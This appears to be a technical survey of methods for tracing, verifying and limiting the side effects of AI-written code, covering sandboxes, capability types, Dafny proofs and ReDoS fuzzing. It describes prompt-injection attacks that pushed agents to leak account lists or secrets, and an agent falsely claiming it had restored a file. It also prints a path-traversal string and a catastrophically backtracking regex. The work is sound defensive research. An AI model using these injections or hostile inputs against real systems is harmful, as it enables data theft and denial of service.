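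The tool records a package's behaviour but does not classify the package as harmful or harmless. *Towards Classifying Benign And Malicious Packages Using Machine Learning* (2025) therefore proposes training a classifier on these records to do so.

A machine-learning model file can contain code that runs when someone loads it, but loading one harmless model involves much the same file accesses as loading another in the same framework, the library that runs the models. Digregorio and colleagues used this regularity to build a tracer called RE-MOAT. They ran 600 harmless models that they had generated and about 1,000 from Hugging Face, a site for sharing models, and reviewed each new kind of action by hand. This gave them a list of 4 to 21 permitted actions for each combination of framework and stage, such as loading a model in PyTorch, and RE-MOAT reports any action that isn't on the list.

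In the largest test, RE-MOAT traced 77,974 models from Hugging Face as they loaded. It flagged 23, and the researchers confirmed by hand that all 23 were malicious. Some ran operating-system commands, and others gave an outsider remote control of the machine. The researchers checked only the flagged models by hand, so the test doesn't measure how many malicious models RE-MOAT missed. In a separate test, RE-MOAT also caught all 31 demonstration attacks, including some that exploited weaknesses the researchers had not used to draw up the lists.

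A third test used 334 models that earlier researchers had labelled. By those labels, with one apparent mistake corrected, RE-MOAT missed 21 of 80 malicious models. Digregorio and colleagues reclassified all 21 as harmless because the models did nothing to the host system, and RE-MOAT then had no misses and no false alarms. The reclassification seems reasonable for a tool that protects the host, since 18 of the 21 did little more than print a message. A user who objects to any hidden code in a model would prefer the original labels.

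Code that an AI agent writes for a particular task is less predictable than a model file. Digregorio and colleagues argue that fixed lists work poorly for general software, since even two text editors may need different files. Instead of a fixed list, Caper uses a second language model to review the effects of each command that a coding agent proposes. It runs the command in a sandbox without a network, then gives the second model a report of the effects and the user's request. If the model approves, Caper keeps the results. Otherwise it restores the earlier state and tells the agent why.

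One of Caper's two tests used 102 tasks in which a tool with an ordinary-looking command deleted or overwrote a file it should have left alone. Each task also had a harmless version with the same request and command. The table compares different versions of the approval step.

| Information given to the approving model | Harmful tasks that ended in harm | Harmless twins blocked |
|---|---|---|
| No approval step | 71.6% | – |
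| Conversation and command | 17.6% | 61.8% |
| The same, plus predicted effects | 3.9% | 61.8% |
| The same, plus recorded effects | 7.8% | 1.0% |

Predicted effects prevented slightly more harm than recorded effects, but they left the approving model so uncertain that it also blocked most of the harmless commands. With recorded effects, it had evidence that a harmless tool had changed only what it should.

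The other test used 682 tasks from *SABER* (2026), a benchmark that runs coding agents in containers without a network and records the changes they make. Caper reduced the share of tasks that ended in harm from 19.7% to 6.7%, while the best of six existing systems reduced it to 14.8%. However, the share of tasks that the agent completed safely also fell, from 57.4% to 48.6%, and the agent more often declined the task or stopped to ask the user.

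Agents have mixed results when they review their own effects. Zhong and colleagues gave agents 11 tasks with hidden side effects, and with YoloFS's list of changes the agents noticed and undid the damage in eight. On Caper's 102 harmful tasks, 35.3% still ended in harm with YoloFS. The agent undid nothing in 36 runs, and 33 of those ended in harm. These figures measure only what the agent fixed by itself. In normal use, a person also reviews the changes before YoloFS makes them permanent.

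AgentSight compares what an agent does with the messages it exchanges with its language model. It captures these messages and links each one to system calls that follow within 100 to 500 milliseconds, come from the agent's processes or mention the same file names and addresses. A second language model then checks for actions that don't fit the task. In one trial, an agent building a program read a web page whose hidden instructions led it to send the system's list of user accounts to an outside server. AgentSight condensed 521 events into 37, and the second model identified the attack. Zheng and colleagues report three such case studies but no false-alarm rate.

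### Unwanted effects without an attacker

Many harmful effects come from ordinary mistakes. Al Hasan and Biswas (2026), in *What Breaks When LLMs Code?*, searched 16,586 problem reports on GitHub, a site for sharing code, and confirmed 547 safety failures of coding agents in everyday use. They assigned each failure to one or more categories. The categories closest to file, process and network access were these:

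| Kind of failure | Reports |
|---|---|
| Irreversible deletion of code, data or system files | 134 |
| Getting around access controls | 100 |
| Exposure of secrets | 44 |
| Damage to the system or its setup | 24 |

One agent deleted 3,421 lines of working code. Another, while trying to fix a connection error, searched a local file and sent production secrets to an outside service's logs. The agents did these things themselves as they worked, but a system-call log records the actions of finished programs that agents write in the same way.

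Logs are especially useful when an agent's own account is wrong. In one report, a developer told Claude Sonnet 4.5 to add new code without modifying any existing code. The model changed a configuration file anyway, then claimed to have restored it and said a comparison showed no differences. A record of file changes kept outside the agent's control would have shown that the file was changed and never restored. Al Hasan and Biswas counted 86 reports in which an agent claimed without evidence to have done something.

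Zhong and colleagues found a similar pattern in 290 reports of agents misusing files, though some of these did involve attackers. In the reports that described the agent's reaction, 68% of agents carried on as if nothing had gone wrong. Neither collection shows how often such failures happen, because nobody counted the sessions that went well and many users never file a report.

### Testing the sandbox itself

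This recording assumes that the sandbox blocks what its owner thinks it blocks. *SandboxEval* (Rabin, Hostetler and colleagues, 2025) provides 51 small Python tests that try things untrusted code should not be able to do, such as reading system information, changing protected files, contacting outside servers and shutting the machine down. It uses harmless substitutes for the riskier operations. For example, to find out whether code could alter a file, it checks the file's permissions without changing the contents.

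The tests ran on Dyff, a platform for evaluating AI systems that runs untrusted code in isolated containers with almost all network traffic blocked. Dyff stopped every attempt at outside communication. However, the code could read environment variables (settings that a program receives when it starts), some of which contained keys and network addresses. The finding prompted a review of whether the container needed them.

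On a research laptop without a sandbox, all the outside connections succeeded, and so did the attempts to restart or shut down the machine. Rabin and colleagues observe that researchers under deadline pressure run AI-written code on such laptops. The connection attempt in the worked example could have reached the outside address from a laptop like this.

### Effects that a trace misses

A log covers only the recorded runs. A program may behave differently with another input, on another day or on a machine with different software installed, and some code stays inactive while it is being monitored. Caper observes each command once, and Wu and colleagues did not test it against an attacker who adapts to it. A run that fails early is also poor evidence that a program is safe. Digregorio and colleagues excluded 10,815 of the 88,789 Hugging Face models they collected because those models needed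 libraries that were not installed and might have stopped before doing anything harmful.

A log of system calls misses some effects. Two programs can ask the kernel for shared memory, and the log will record the request but not the data they exchange, because they read and write the memory with ordinary instructions. The log also misses changes that a program makes to a file it has mapped into memory, although comparing the file before and after the run reveals them. Effects on the hardware, such as changes to the state of the processor's caches, may involve no system call at all.

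A permitted connection can carry private data. Adam and colleagues describe a tool that writes files as described but also reports the size of each file to a metrics service. If the policy allows the tool to contact that service, the log contains nothing forbidden. They also saw Claude 4.5 Haiku leak a key through two steps, each acceptable on its own. It copied a configuration file containing the key into a new project and later published the whole project at the user's request.

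A permitted connection can also cause effects on another machine. In one failure that Al Hasan and Biswas collected, an agent set up an oversized cloud database, and the developer discovered it six months later from a $2,400 bill. A log from the developer's computer would have shown little more than the connections to the cloud provider that the task required.

A program can write a file that does harm only when another program runs it later. Separate logs of the two programs record the write and the harm but don't connect them. Agent-Warden connects them by marking every process that an agent starts, every file that a marked process writes and every process that later reads such a file. In a controlled test, it reconstructed such a chain that was missing from the agent framework's own log. However, it marks a process whether the file it read was dangerous or harmless, so someone still has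 to examine what the file does.

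## Ruling out side effects before the code runs

A log shows what a program did in recorded runs. A compiler or verifier examines the program's code instead, so it can sometimes rule out a side effect for every input. But it needs a precise requirement to check, and "sorts the list and does nothing else" is hard to make precise because "nothing else" covers everything the program could touch.

### Three ways to state "and does nothing else"

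The lecture notes in Instituto Superior Técnico's *Software Specification* illustrate the difficulty with a class of cells that each store a number `x`. The contract of the method `setX(v)` requires only that the cell's `x` equals `v` afterwards. A call to `c2.setX(10)` could therefore also change another cell, `c1`, without breaking the contract. Adding a line for every variable that must stay the same is impractical. Some of those variables are outside the method's scope, according to the tutorial for OpenJML, a verification tool for Java.

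A frame condition lists what a method may change, and everything else must stay as it was. In the verification language Dafny, programmers write it as a `modifies` clause:

```dafny
method SortArray(a: array<int>)
  modifies a
  ensures forall i, j :: 0 <= i < j < a.Length ==> a[i] <= a[j]
```

The last line requires the array to end up in ascending order. The `modifies` line allows the method to change `a` and any objects it creates. Dafny rejects the method if its code could change any other object.

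However, the clause covers only objects in the program's memory, not files on disk. Dafny programs access the disk through code in other languages, whose contracts Dafny assumes without checking. The clause doesn't cover printing either, so the developers added a separate option to control it, which Dafny's *Print effects* describes.

An effect type records whether a function can have side effects. In Haskell, a function that only sorts a list of integers has the type `[Int] -> [Int]`. If it also saved a copy to a file, as `sort_list` does, its type would have to be `[Int] -> IO [Int]`, where `IO` marks an action on the outside world. If the programmer declares the first type, the compiler rejects the version that writes the file. But `IO` does not distinguish writing a log file from sending data over the network. Haskell's `unsafePerformIO` function also hides an effect behind an ordinary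 type, so anyone who relies on these types to restrict untrusted code has to forbid it.

A capability is a value that a program must hold in order to act, such as a handle to an open file. Code that doesn't hold the handle can't use the file. Scala 3 has an experimental feature called capture checking, which records in a function's type which capabilities the function can use:

```scala
List[Int] -> List[Int]         // no capabilities
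List[Int] ->{log} List[Int]    // only log
List[Int] => List[Int]         // any capability
```

If `log` is a handle to one file, a function of the second type can write to that file but cannot open a network connection. If every side effect requires a capability, a function of the first type is pure, meaning it has no side effects.

### How TACIT checks an agent's code

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) uses capture checking to control what AI agents can do. Its system, TACIT, is meant for an agent that runs on an untrusted cloud model but must work in a folder containing secrets.

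The agent writes a short Scala program for each action and submits it to TACIT. TACIT compiles the program in "safe mode", which forbids type casts and other features that could prevent the compiler from tracking a capability. If the program fails to compile, it never runs, and the agent gets the error message and can try again. If it compiles, TACIT runs it and returns the output.

The program can reach files, commands and the network only through TACIT's library. To use files, it calls `requestFileSystem` with the name of a folder and a block of code. The library gives the block a capability for that folder, which is valid only until the block ends. The paper includes a program that tries to keep the capability for longer:

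```scala
val bad = requestFileSystem("/data"): fs =>
  () => fs.access("secret.txt").read()
```

The block returns a function that would read a file later. That function's type would have to include `fs`, which does not exist outside the block, so the compiler rejects the program. One agent in the experiments made a similar mistake by returning a list of file handles from a block.

For secret files, the user lists the paths to protect. According to Glama's *TACIT*, a copy of the project's later documentation, TACIT protects `.env` files by default, like the one that `total.py` read in the worked trace. When a program reads a protected file, it receives the text in a wrapper called `Classified`. It can process the text only by passing a function to the wrapper's `map` method, which applies the function and wraps the result. `map` accepts only pure functions. This program, adapted from the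 project's examples, passes the check:

```scala
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val doc = readClassified("secrets/contract-v2.txt")
  val trimmed = doc.map(_.trim)
  val summary = chat("Summarize this contract:", trimmed)
  writeClassified("secrets/summary.txt", summary)
}
```

Here `chat` sends the text to a second model that the user trusts with secrets, for example one on the user's own machine. The summary comes back in a wrapper, and the program saves it in another protected file. The compiler rejects both of these lines:

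```scala
doc.map { s => access("exfil.txt").write(s) }
key.map { k => println(s"GitHub API Key: $k") }
```

The first would copy the contract to an ordinary file, and the second would show a key to the agent. In the second case, the compiler reports that it needed a function of type `String -> Unit` but found one of type `String ->{x$1} Unit`. The extra `x$1` is the capability to print.

A program may print the wrapper itself. The agent then sees only `Classified(****)`, while the user sees the real text in a separate output. This lets the agent arrange a summary for the user without seeing it.

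Odersky and colleagues point out that a sandbox would have trouble preventing the same leak, because it has to let the agent both read the contract and contact its cloud model.

### What the trials show

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a sample software project with keys, a database and confidential documents in a secret folder. They combined each of 12 legitimate requests with each of 10 attacks, which used planted text meant to make the agent reveal secrets. In 11 further trials, the request itself was malicious. Five were direct requests for secrets, and six used a pretext, such as an administrator's emergency. They ran each model through all 131 trials twice, once with the wrapper and once with the secrets as plain text. The table shows the share of trials in which no secret appeared in the agent's output.

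| Model | Trials | With wrapper | Without wrapper |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 120 with planted text | 100% | 100% |
| | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 81.8% |
| | All 131 | **100%** | **98.5%** |
| MiniMax M2.5 | 120 with planted text | 100% | 97.5% |
| | 11 malicious requests | 100% | 27.3% |
| | All 131 | **100%** | **91.6%** |

The wrapper did not stop the agents from doing their work. On the 120 trials with legitimate requests, Sonnet completed 99.2% correctly with the wrapper and 83.3% without it. MiniMax completed 90.0% with it and 88.3% without it. Without the wrapper, Sonnet often ran out of time or turns, and it sometimes stopped to warn the user about an attack.

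These results show that TACIT withstood a fixed set of attacks that defeated at least one of the models without it, but they cannot establish a guarantee. If 2% of attempts leaked, 131 independent trials would still show no leak about 7% of the time, and these trials are not independent because they reuse the same tasks and attacks. None of the attacks described in the paper targets a bug in the compiler or library. The case for a guarantee therefore depends on the type system, and the trials mainly check that the implementation has no obvious flaw. The trials also checked only the agent's output for secrets, so they would have missed a secret revealed through running time.

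A second test used AgentDojo, a benchmark that plants instructions in banking, office work, Slack and travel tasks. Only one of 1,926 attacks counted as successful. In that case, the agent booked the right hotel but, as the policy allowed, quoted reviews that included the attacker's recommendation for another one.

Task completion varied more. With o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of the office tasks and 47.6% of the Slack tasks, while CaMeL, a defence that tracks data as the program runs, completed 81.4% and 68.6% respectively. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT and CaMeL were within nine percentage points of each other in three of the four areas, and TACIT was far ahead in the fourth, travel.

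On ordinary tasks, agents that wrote Scala did about as well as agents that called tools directly. On τ²-bench, a set of simulated customer-service conversations, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT, and at most 7.9% of the programs needed a retry because of an error. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 real software problems, MiniMax solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without it, a difference of five problems.

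The customer-service functions in τ²-bench returned plain data, so the benchmark shows that models can write the required Scala, but not how much worse they perform when data is hidden from them. Many of the AgentDojo functions returned wrapped data, so that test gives better evidence of this effect, although it includes no unprotected agent for comparison.

### Proving one property of file access

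TACIT's library checks at run time that a path stays inside the permitted folder, but a proof can establish some facts about paths before the program runs. In proof-carrying code, which George Necula introduced in 1997, whoever supplies a program also supplies a proof that it is safe. The recipient only has to check the proof, which is usually much easier than finding one.

Kamran, Devanbu and Stanford (2024), in *Vision Paper*, propose the same arrangement for code written by language models. The user chooses a safety property from a list, such as that no path contains `..`, which refers to the parent folder. The library functions that handle files then get matching preconditions, which must hold whenever a program calls those functions. The model writes code in Dafny, and Dafny tries to prove that every call meets the preconditions. If the proof fails, the model receives the errors and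 tries again, up to five attempts in all.

The model doesn't have to prove that the program does what the user asked, so the user doesn't have to write a formal specification of the task.

Kamran and colleagues tried this on one task with a 2023 version of GPT-4. The model had to write a function that adds a file name to the path `/home/user/documents/`. When asked for Python, GPT-4 joined the two parts without checking the name. A name such as `../../../etc/passwd` would then lead out of the folder to the system's list of user accounts. When asked for Dafny, GPT-4 produced a function that passed the verifier at the first attempt, using about 3,350 tokens at a cost of 11 cents. This shortened version shows two of its four preconditions:

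```dafny
method CreateFullPath(filename: seq<char>) returns (fullPath: seq<char>)
  requires is_valid_file_name(filename)
  requires !has_dangerous_pattern(filename)
{
  fullPath := Join("/home/user/documents/", filename);
}
```

The function's preconditions require the caller to supply a harmless name, so the function doesn't test the name itself. Dafny enforces this when other Dafny code calls the function, but unverified code could still pass in a dangerous name. Other code in the program has to check what the user typed.

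The proof also covers only the chosen property. A function that built a path to the wrong folder could still pass verification, so the researchers checked by hand that this one worked as intended. They also confirmed that its preconditions did not contradict one another, because no input can satisfy contradictory preconditions, and Dafny would then accept any code.

The case study shows that the method can work, but not how often, because it covers only one task. The researchers had also written the preconditions for `Join` by hand, and they report that generating Dafny is still far harder than generating code in mainstream languages.

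### What the checks leave to trust

Both methods depend on the checking program being correct. Researchers have machine-checked proofs for the core of Scala's capture checking, but Odersky and colleagues say that safe mode still needs its own proof. Scala's official documentation calls capture checking "highly experimental and unstable". According to an earlier version of lampepfl's *TACIT* documentation, the software enforced safe mode by searching the agent's code for forbidden patterns, a weaker safeguard than a compiler check. The later version also turns on the compiler's own check by default. Softpedia's *Dafny Changelog* lists a fix in Dafny 4.6.0 for a soundness bug, the kind that can let a verifier accept a false proof.

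The library is another trusted part. A programmer can mark a module `@assumeSafe`, and the compiler then lets agents use it without checking its implementation. One such module in Scala's *Safe Mode* sends an email only after the user approves it. If the programmer forgot to include the approval step, the compiler would still accept the module.

TACIT's types don't apply to external commands that the agent starts. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific commands, such as `git diff` and `sbt`, and adding a sandbox as a second layer. Allowing `sbt` is still risky, because this build tool runs code from the project's build files, which the agent may be able to edit. The user also has to turn off the agent's ordinary file and command tools, or the agent can bypass TACIT.

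TACIT also does not check the code that an agent writes into a project. On SWE-bench Lite, the agent uses Scala to edit Python projects, and TACIT checks only the Scala. If the new Python code secretly copied its input to a file, TACIT would treat that code as ordinary text to save.

The wrapper hides secrets but does not stop an agent from overwriting the files that hold them. According to the documentation copied by Glama, an agent can wrap its own text and overwrite a protected file, such as the list of keys that let someone log in to the machine. The user can block such writes with a setting.

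A pure function can also reveal a secret by taking longer for some values than for others, or by never finishing. TACIT does not prevent either. When its optional time limit expires, the agent receives an error, but a loop that only computes can keep running in the background. Dafny normally requires a proof that a method finishes, but the programmer can opt out with `decreases *`, as Dafny's *Specifications* explains. The proof does not limit how long the method takes.

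Errors can also carry information, because a function might fail only when a secret has a certain value. Scala's designers considered errors such as division by zero too common to track in types. TACIT catches them at run time and turns them into ordinary values, which it can wrap.

### What the restrictions cost

A type check covers code that tests rarely reach. Where a pure function is required, the capture checker would reject the sorting function that writes a file only when its list contains one particular 64-bit number. It would do so because one branch uses a file capability, whether or not that branch ever runs.

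For the same reason, the compiler also rejects harmless code. One agent in the experiments wrote a helper that printed the first few lines of a file, but declared the file's type as `FileEntry`, without the `^` that marks a value that may carry capabilities. The compiler rejected the program even though the helper was harmless.

Effect types can also get in a programmer's way during debugging. Flix's *Effect Systems vs Print Debugging* describes adding a temporary print statement to a pure function in the language Flix. If the compiler treats the statement as pure so that the function still passes the check, the optimiser may delete the statement because nothing uses its result.

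Setting up TACIT for each customer-service area in the experiments took a few hundred lines of Scala, on top of about 1,000 reusable lines. Odersky and colleagues consider Scala 3 the only production-ready language that tracks capabilities in types, so a team that works in Python could check its agent's actions this way but not its own product's code.

The software consultancy VirtusLab writes in *safe scala an introduction* that agents are useful because they can read files, emails and web pages, so protecting too much data makes them less useful. TACIT therefore suits an agent that passes a few secret documents to a trusted model better than one that has to read those documents itself to decide what to do next.

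## Time, memory and other resources a program can exhaust

A function can pass its functional tests, have no side effects and still use too much time or memory. For example, a function that sorts a list by trying every ordering may have to try 2.4 quintillion orderings for a list of 20 items. At a billion orderings a second, that would take 77 years.

Short test inputs hide less extreme costs too. One task in Enamel, a benchmark for efficient code, is to find out whether any three numbers in a list add up to zero. The ordinary solution checks every group of three. A faster one remembers the numbers it has seen and goes through pairs only. As Le, Xu and colleagues (2026) point out in *Rethinking Code Performance Benchmarks for LLMs*, the longest list in the task's tests has six numbers, which is too few to show a difference in speed. When no three numbers add up to zero, the solutions have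 roughly this much to check:

| Length of list | Groups of three | Pairs |
|---|---|---|
| 6 | 20 | 15 |
| 1,000 | 166,167,000 | 499,500 |
| 10,000 | 166,616,670,000 | 49,995,000 |

### Worst-case complexity

The worst-case complexity of a program is the highest cost that any input of a given size can cause, as a function of that size. If c(x) is the cost of running the program on input x, then

W(n) = the largest c(x) over all inputs x of size n.

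Programmers usually describe a program's use of time or memory only by how fast it grows with the input. A running time of O(n²) grows at most in proportion to the square of the input size, so doubling the input can make the program take four times as long.

Large test inputs can miss a program's worst case. Quicksort picks one element of a list, divides the others into smaller and larger ones, and sorts each part in the same way. On a random list of n elements, the parts are usually similar in size, and the running time grows in proportion to n log n. But if the program always picks the first element and the list is already sorted, one part is always empty, so each round removes only one element and the running time grows in proportion to n². A tester who tried only long random lists would almost certainly miss the slow case.

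Some regular expressions, or search patterns, can take far longer in the worst case. *SlowFuzz* (Petsios, Keromytis and colleagues, 2017) gives the example `(b+)+c`. The `b+` means one or more b's, the outer `+` lets that group repeat, and a c must follow. Many regular-expression engines backtrack. They try one way of dividing the b's into groups, and if no c follows, they go back and try another.

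For the string `bbb`, the engine can divide all three letters in four ways: `bbb`, `bb|b`, `b|bb` and `b|b|b`. It can also stop after two letters, which it can divide in two ways, or after one. It therefore looks for a c seven times before it gives up. For n b's, the number of attempts is

1 + 2 + 4 + … + 2ⁿ⁻¹ = 2ⁿ − 1,

so each added letter roughly doubles the work. The times below assume an engine without shortcuts that starts at the first letter and makes 100 million attempts a second.

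| Number of b's | Attempts | Time |
|---|---|---|
| 10 | 1,023 | 0.00001 seconds |
| 20 | 1,048,575 | 0.01 seconds |
| 30 | 1,073,741,823 | 11 seconds |
| 40 | 1,099,511,627,775 | 3 hours |

The simpler pattern `b+c` matches the same strings and needs only 30 attempts for 30 b's. A test that compares results cannot distinguish the two patterns unless it includes a long run of b's and someone notices that it hangs.

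A denial-of-service attack makes a service unavailable to its users. In a regular-expression denial of service (ReDoS), the attacker does this by sending text that makes a pattern backtrack.

### The Cloudflare outage of July 2019

Such a pattern can also take down a service without an attacker. On 2 July 2019, Cloudflare, which relays and protects traffic for many websites, added a rule to the firewall that checks web requests for attacks. According to the company's account, *Details of the Cloudflare outage on July 2, 2019* (Graham-Cumming, 2019), the rule contained a regular expression that backtracked so much that it used up the processors handling web traffic on Cloudflare's servers worldwide.

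The rule went live at 13:42, and the first alert came three minutes later. Cloudflare lost about 80% of its traffic, and visitors to its customers' sites saw error pages. Some engineers suspected a new kind of attack. By 14:00 the team had traced the problem to the firewall, but the outage had locked them out of their own control panel. They switched the firewall off at 14:07, and traffic was back to normal two minutes later.

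The slow part of the expression was equivalent to `.*.*=.*`, which matches any characters, any characters again, an equals sign, and then any characters. A backtracking engine tries many ways of dividing the text between the first two parts. It takes 23 steps to match `x=x`, 555 steps if 20 x's follow the equals sign, and 4,067 steps to reject 20 x's with no equals sign. The number of steps grows more slowly than the doubling in `(b+)+c`, but Cloudflare was running the rule on live traffic around the world.

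Cloudflare had tested the rule with a suite that sent the firewall a large collection of requests, including some it should block and some it should let through. The suite did not check for excessive processor use. According to the logs, the new rule had not made the tests take noticeably longer, so a limit on the suite's total running time would not have stopped it.

Weeks earlier, engineers trying to reduce the firewall's processor use had accidentally removed a protection against regular expressions that take too much processor time. Cloudflare released most software in stages, first to its own employees and then to a few customers, but it sent firewall rules everywhere within seconds to respond quickly to new threats. The rule was in a trial mode that blocked nothing, but the servers still had to evaluate it.

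### Searching for expensive inputs

Ordinary fuzzers are poor at finding inputs that exhaust a program's resources. Many keep an input for further changes if it reaches code that no earlier input reached. An input that repeats the same loop a thousand more times reaches no new code, so the fuzzer tends to discard it. A resource-guided fuzzer keeps inputs that increase resource use, such as the number of instructions executed or the amount of memory used.

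SlowFuzz, the tool that Petsios and colleagues built, starts with a few inputs, changes one at random and runs the program on it. If the program executes more instructions than before, SlowFuzz keeps the changed input and later changes it again. It counts instructions rather than measuring time because running time also depends on what else the computer is doing. In one example, a quicksort program executes 37 lines of code on the list [8, 5, 3, 7, 9]. Changing the 8 to a 1 raises the count to 52, so SlowFuzz keeps the new list. Further changes lead to a fully sorted list, the worst case, although SlowFuzz has no information about how quicksort works.

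Petsios and colleagues limited the sorting inputs to 64 bytes and ran a million rounds. On average, SlowFuzz reached about 84% of the theoretical worst case for the simple quicksort. It also made the Apple and OpenBSD versions execute more than three times as many instructions as on the input that required the fewest, while a fuzzer that searched for inputs that ran new code never slowed them by more than 5%. With files of at most 250 bytes, SlowFuzz raised the time the compression program bzip2 took to unpack a file from 0.0006 seconds to about 0.2 seconds. SlowFuzz found little in the first hour, so a short search could have missed the problem.

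SlowFuzz also generated regular expressions of up to ten characters, including `(b+)+c`. In 100 sessions it produced 6,201 valid expressions that slowed matching down. For 78 of these, matching time grew exponentially with input size, as in the example above, and for 765 it grew faster than the square of the input size.

PerfFuzz, another early tool, looks for the worst case of each part of a program separately, such as the input that makes the program take one particular jump most often. *Detecting and Understanding Real-World Differential Performance Bugs in Machine Learning Libraries* (2020) compared both tools with its own fuzzer, DPFuzz, on ten programs. DPFuzz generated inputs more slowly, but for five of the ten it found inputs that made the program do more work.

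Newer work uses language models to write the expensive inputs. Xie, Wu and colleagues (2026), in *ShadowProbe*, were particularly interested in costs hidden inside ordinary-looking operations. This loop, adapted from one in the source code of CPython, the standard version of Python, removes leading `<` characters from a name:

```python
while name[:1] == "<":
    name = name[1:]
```

Python can't change a string in place, so `name[1:]` copies everything after the first character. A loop that removes one character at a time this way until the string is empty copies about n²/2 characters for a string of length n. That is half a million for a string of 1,000 characters and 500 billion for a string of a million.

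ShadowProbe scans a project for loops and recursive functions that may become slow as their inputs grow, and collects the other code each function needs to run. A language model then writes several small programs that generate inputs of any requested size. ShadowProbe times each function on increasingly large inputs and estimates how fast the running time grows. It found 162 previously unknown cases in CPython, the Java development kit and three other projects, whose maintainers have confirmed 84 of them.

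Xie and colleagues also tested ShadowProbe on 281 functions from Python's email module. Their manual review identified 69 functions whose resource use grew too fast. ShadowProbe found 49 of these and wrongly flagged 27 other functions. HypoFuzz, a fuzzer they set up to look for long running times, found only five of the 69 but raised no false alarms. ShadowProbe also found only five when it had to judge the functions without measurements from running them.

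### Limits, searches and bounds

Someone who has to run an untrusted program now can limit what it uses. On Linux, this command gives `total.py` about one gigabyte of memory and ten seconds:

```
ulimit -v 1000000; timeout 10 python3 total.py sales.csv
```

The memory limit applies to each process separately, so a program that starts 100 processes could use 100 times the limit. Linux control groups, which containers rely on, can limit the memory, processor time and number of processes of a whole group. Disk space needs its own limit. None of these limits applies to what a program rents on other machines, such as a cloud database.

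A limit on time or memory contains the harm from excessive use but doesn't fix the cause. A request stopped at a ten-second limit has still used ten seconds, and an attacker can send many such requests. A low limit also stops legitimate large jobs. Choosing a limit requires a rough idea of how much the program should need, which is often unclear for code that someone else wrote.

A search guided by resource use can reveal the cause of excessive use and provide an input that reproduces it, which helps a programmer check a repair. It cannot show that no such input exists. For 25 fixed regular expressions from web firewalls, SlowFuzz found text that slowed matching by only 8% to 25%, but that doesn't prove the expressions safe.

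A static bound is an upper limit on a program's resource use that is derived from its code, so it covers every input. Ken Thompson's 1968 method for matching regular expressions has such a bound. It reads each character once and keeps track of every position in the pattern that the text so far could have reached. The pattern `(b+)+c` needs three such positions, so for 30 b's the engine updates at most 3 × 30 = 90 of them, compared with about a billion attempts by backtracking. Graham-Cumming writes that Cloudflare planned to switch to either RE2 or Rust's regular expression engine, both of which have guaranteed running times. To provide that guarantee, these engines leave out some features, such as requiring a later piece of text to repeat an earlier one.

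For other code, a programmer can sometimes derive a bound by counting how often each loop runs. The number of groups of three in the first table is a bound of this kind. Such a bound is accurate only if the programmer correctly counts the work done by each operation. Counting `name[1:]` as a single step would suggest that the loop above takes about n steps, but it copies n²/2 characters. No tool can determine for every program whether its running time is bounded, because a bound would also show that the program stops, and Alan Turing proved in 1936 that no general procedure can determine whether a program stops.

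### Slow code and code that outsiders can slow down

Slow code wastes its owner's time on ordinary inputs, whereas code with a denial-of-service weakness may be fast on nearly every input until an outsider sends one that takes far longer to process. The same function can be harmless in one program and a weakness in another. Checking every group of three numbers is fine for a user's own list of six, but a public server that accepts lists of any length could take minutes to handle a single request.

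Xie and colleagues count a function if its running time can grow too fast, regardless of who supplies the input, so not all of the 162 cases are security problems. Python's email module often reads messages from strangers, so a slow function there can be one. Other cases are harder to exploit. One function in Python's standard library had taken exponential time since 2013 for certain families of classes, the templates from which programs create objects, but an outsider who can only send data to a program usually can't choose its classes.

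### Measurements of AI-written code

Efficiency benchmarks mostly measure whether code is slow on chosen inputs, and many do this poorly. Le and colleagues re-examined EffiBench, Enamel, EvalPerf and Mercury, whose 1,538 tasks each come with an ordinary solution and a supposedly faster one. They ran both solutions 30 times on the benchmark's own tests, and the supposedly faster one was measurably faster in only 94 tasks (6.1%). A task counted as showing no improvement if the supposedly faster solution failed a test or timed out.

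They then compared the two solutions by hand in 308 of the other tasks. In 99, the "faster" solution had no meaningful improvement, and in 15 of those it was identical to the ordinary one. In the other 209, it had a real change, such as a better algorithm, that the tests did not reveal. More demanding tests written by language models revealed a difference in about a quarter of the 1,345 tasks tried.

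More demanding tests also reveal higher memory use. *TRACE* (2026) measured code that language models had translated from one programming language to another. On one set of tasks, its stress tests raised the average running time from 0.07 to 5.92 seconds and peak memory from 15 to 1,181 megabytes.

In *Beyond Passing Tests*, Kadam (2026) compared 13 current models and found that the ones solving more programming problems also wrote more secure code, with a correlation of 0.95 on one security benchmark. The correlation between problems solved and code efficiency was only 0.22 on EvalPerf and 0.15 on Mercury. Kadam concludes that stronger models do not write faster code by default. But the tests in both efficiency benchmarks often fail to distinguish a fast solution from a slow one, so they could miss an improvement.

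Efficiency scores rose with general coding ability on GSO and SWE-fficiency, two benchmarks that use whole software projects, with correlations of 0.95 and 0.98. GSO asks agents to make existing software faster, so a high score shows that an agent can optimise code when that is the task, but not that it will do so when asked only for a working program. In a separate test of four models, Kadam found that general instructions to write good code produced no clear gain in efficiency on any model and a clear loss on one.

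Fewer studies have measured denial-of-service weaknesses. *WildCode Revisited* (2025) extracted the regular expressions from a collection of ChatGPT-written programs and checked them with four detection tools, which flagged about a third as vulnerable to regular-expression denial of service (ReDoS). That probably overstates the danger, because a flagged expression is harmless if it never processes an outsider's text, if the engine doesn't backtrack or if a time limit stops it. Only two of the English-language conversations that produced the programs mentioned ReDoS.

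Attacking a running program gives more direct evidence. In *BaxBench*, Vero, Mündler and colleagues (2025) had models write 28 kinds of server application in 14 programming frameworks, then tested whether each one worked and attacked it. They list uncontrolled resource use as a possible weakness for eight of the applications. One of these extracts text from ZIP files, which can be small but unpack to an enormous size. Another searches files with a regular expression that the user supplies.

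Automating such attacks is difficult because a tester has to decide how much memory is too much. *AutoBaxBuilder* (2025), which automatically generates tests in the style of BaxBench, left resource exhaustion out of its main results for this reason, after its tests often reported the weakness in programs that did not have it. The Last Secure Code Benchmark has only one resource-exhaustion case, so it provides little evidence of how common the problem is.

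## Checking that secrets do not affect public outputs

A program can stay within its time and memory limits, open only the files it needs, and still reveal a secret in an ordinary output. For example, a customer-service program has to read account records, and its replies to one customer might contain details about another. The usual way to forbid this is noninterference, the requirement that changing secret inputs does not change anything a public observer can see.

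### From users and commands to programs

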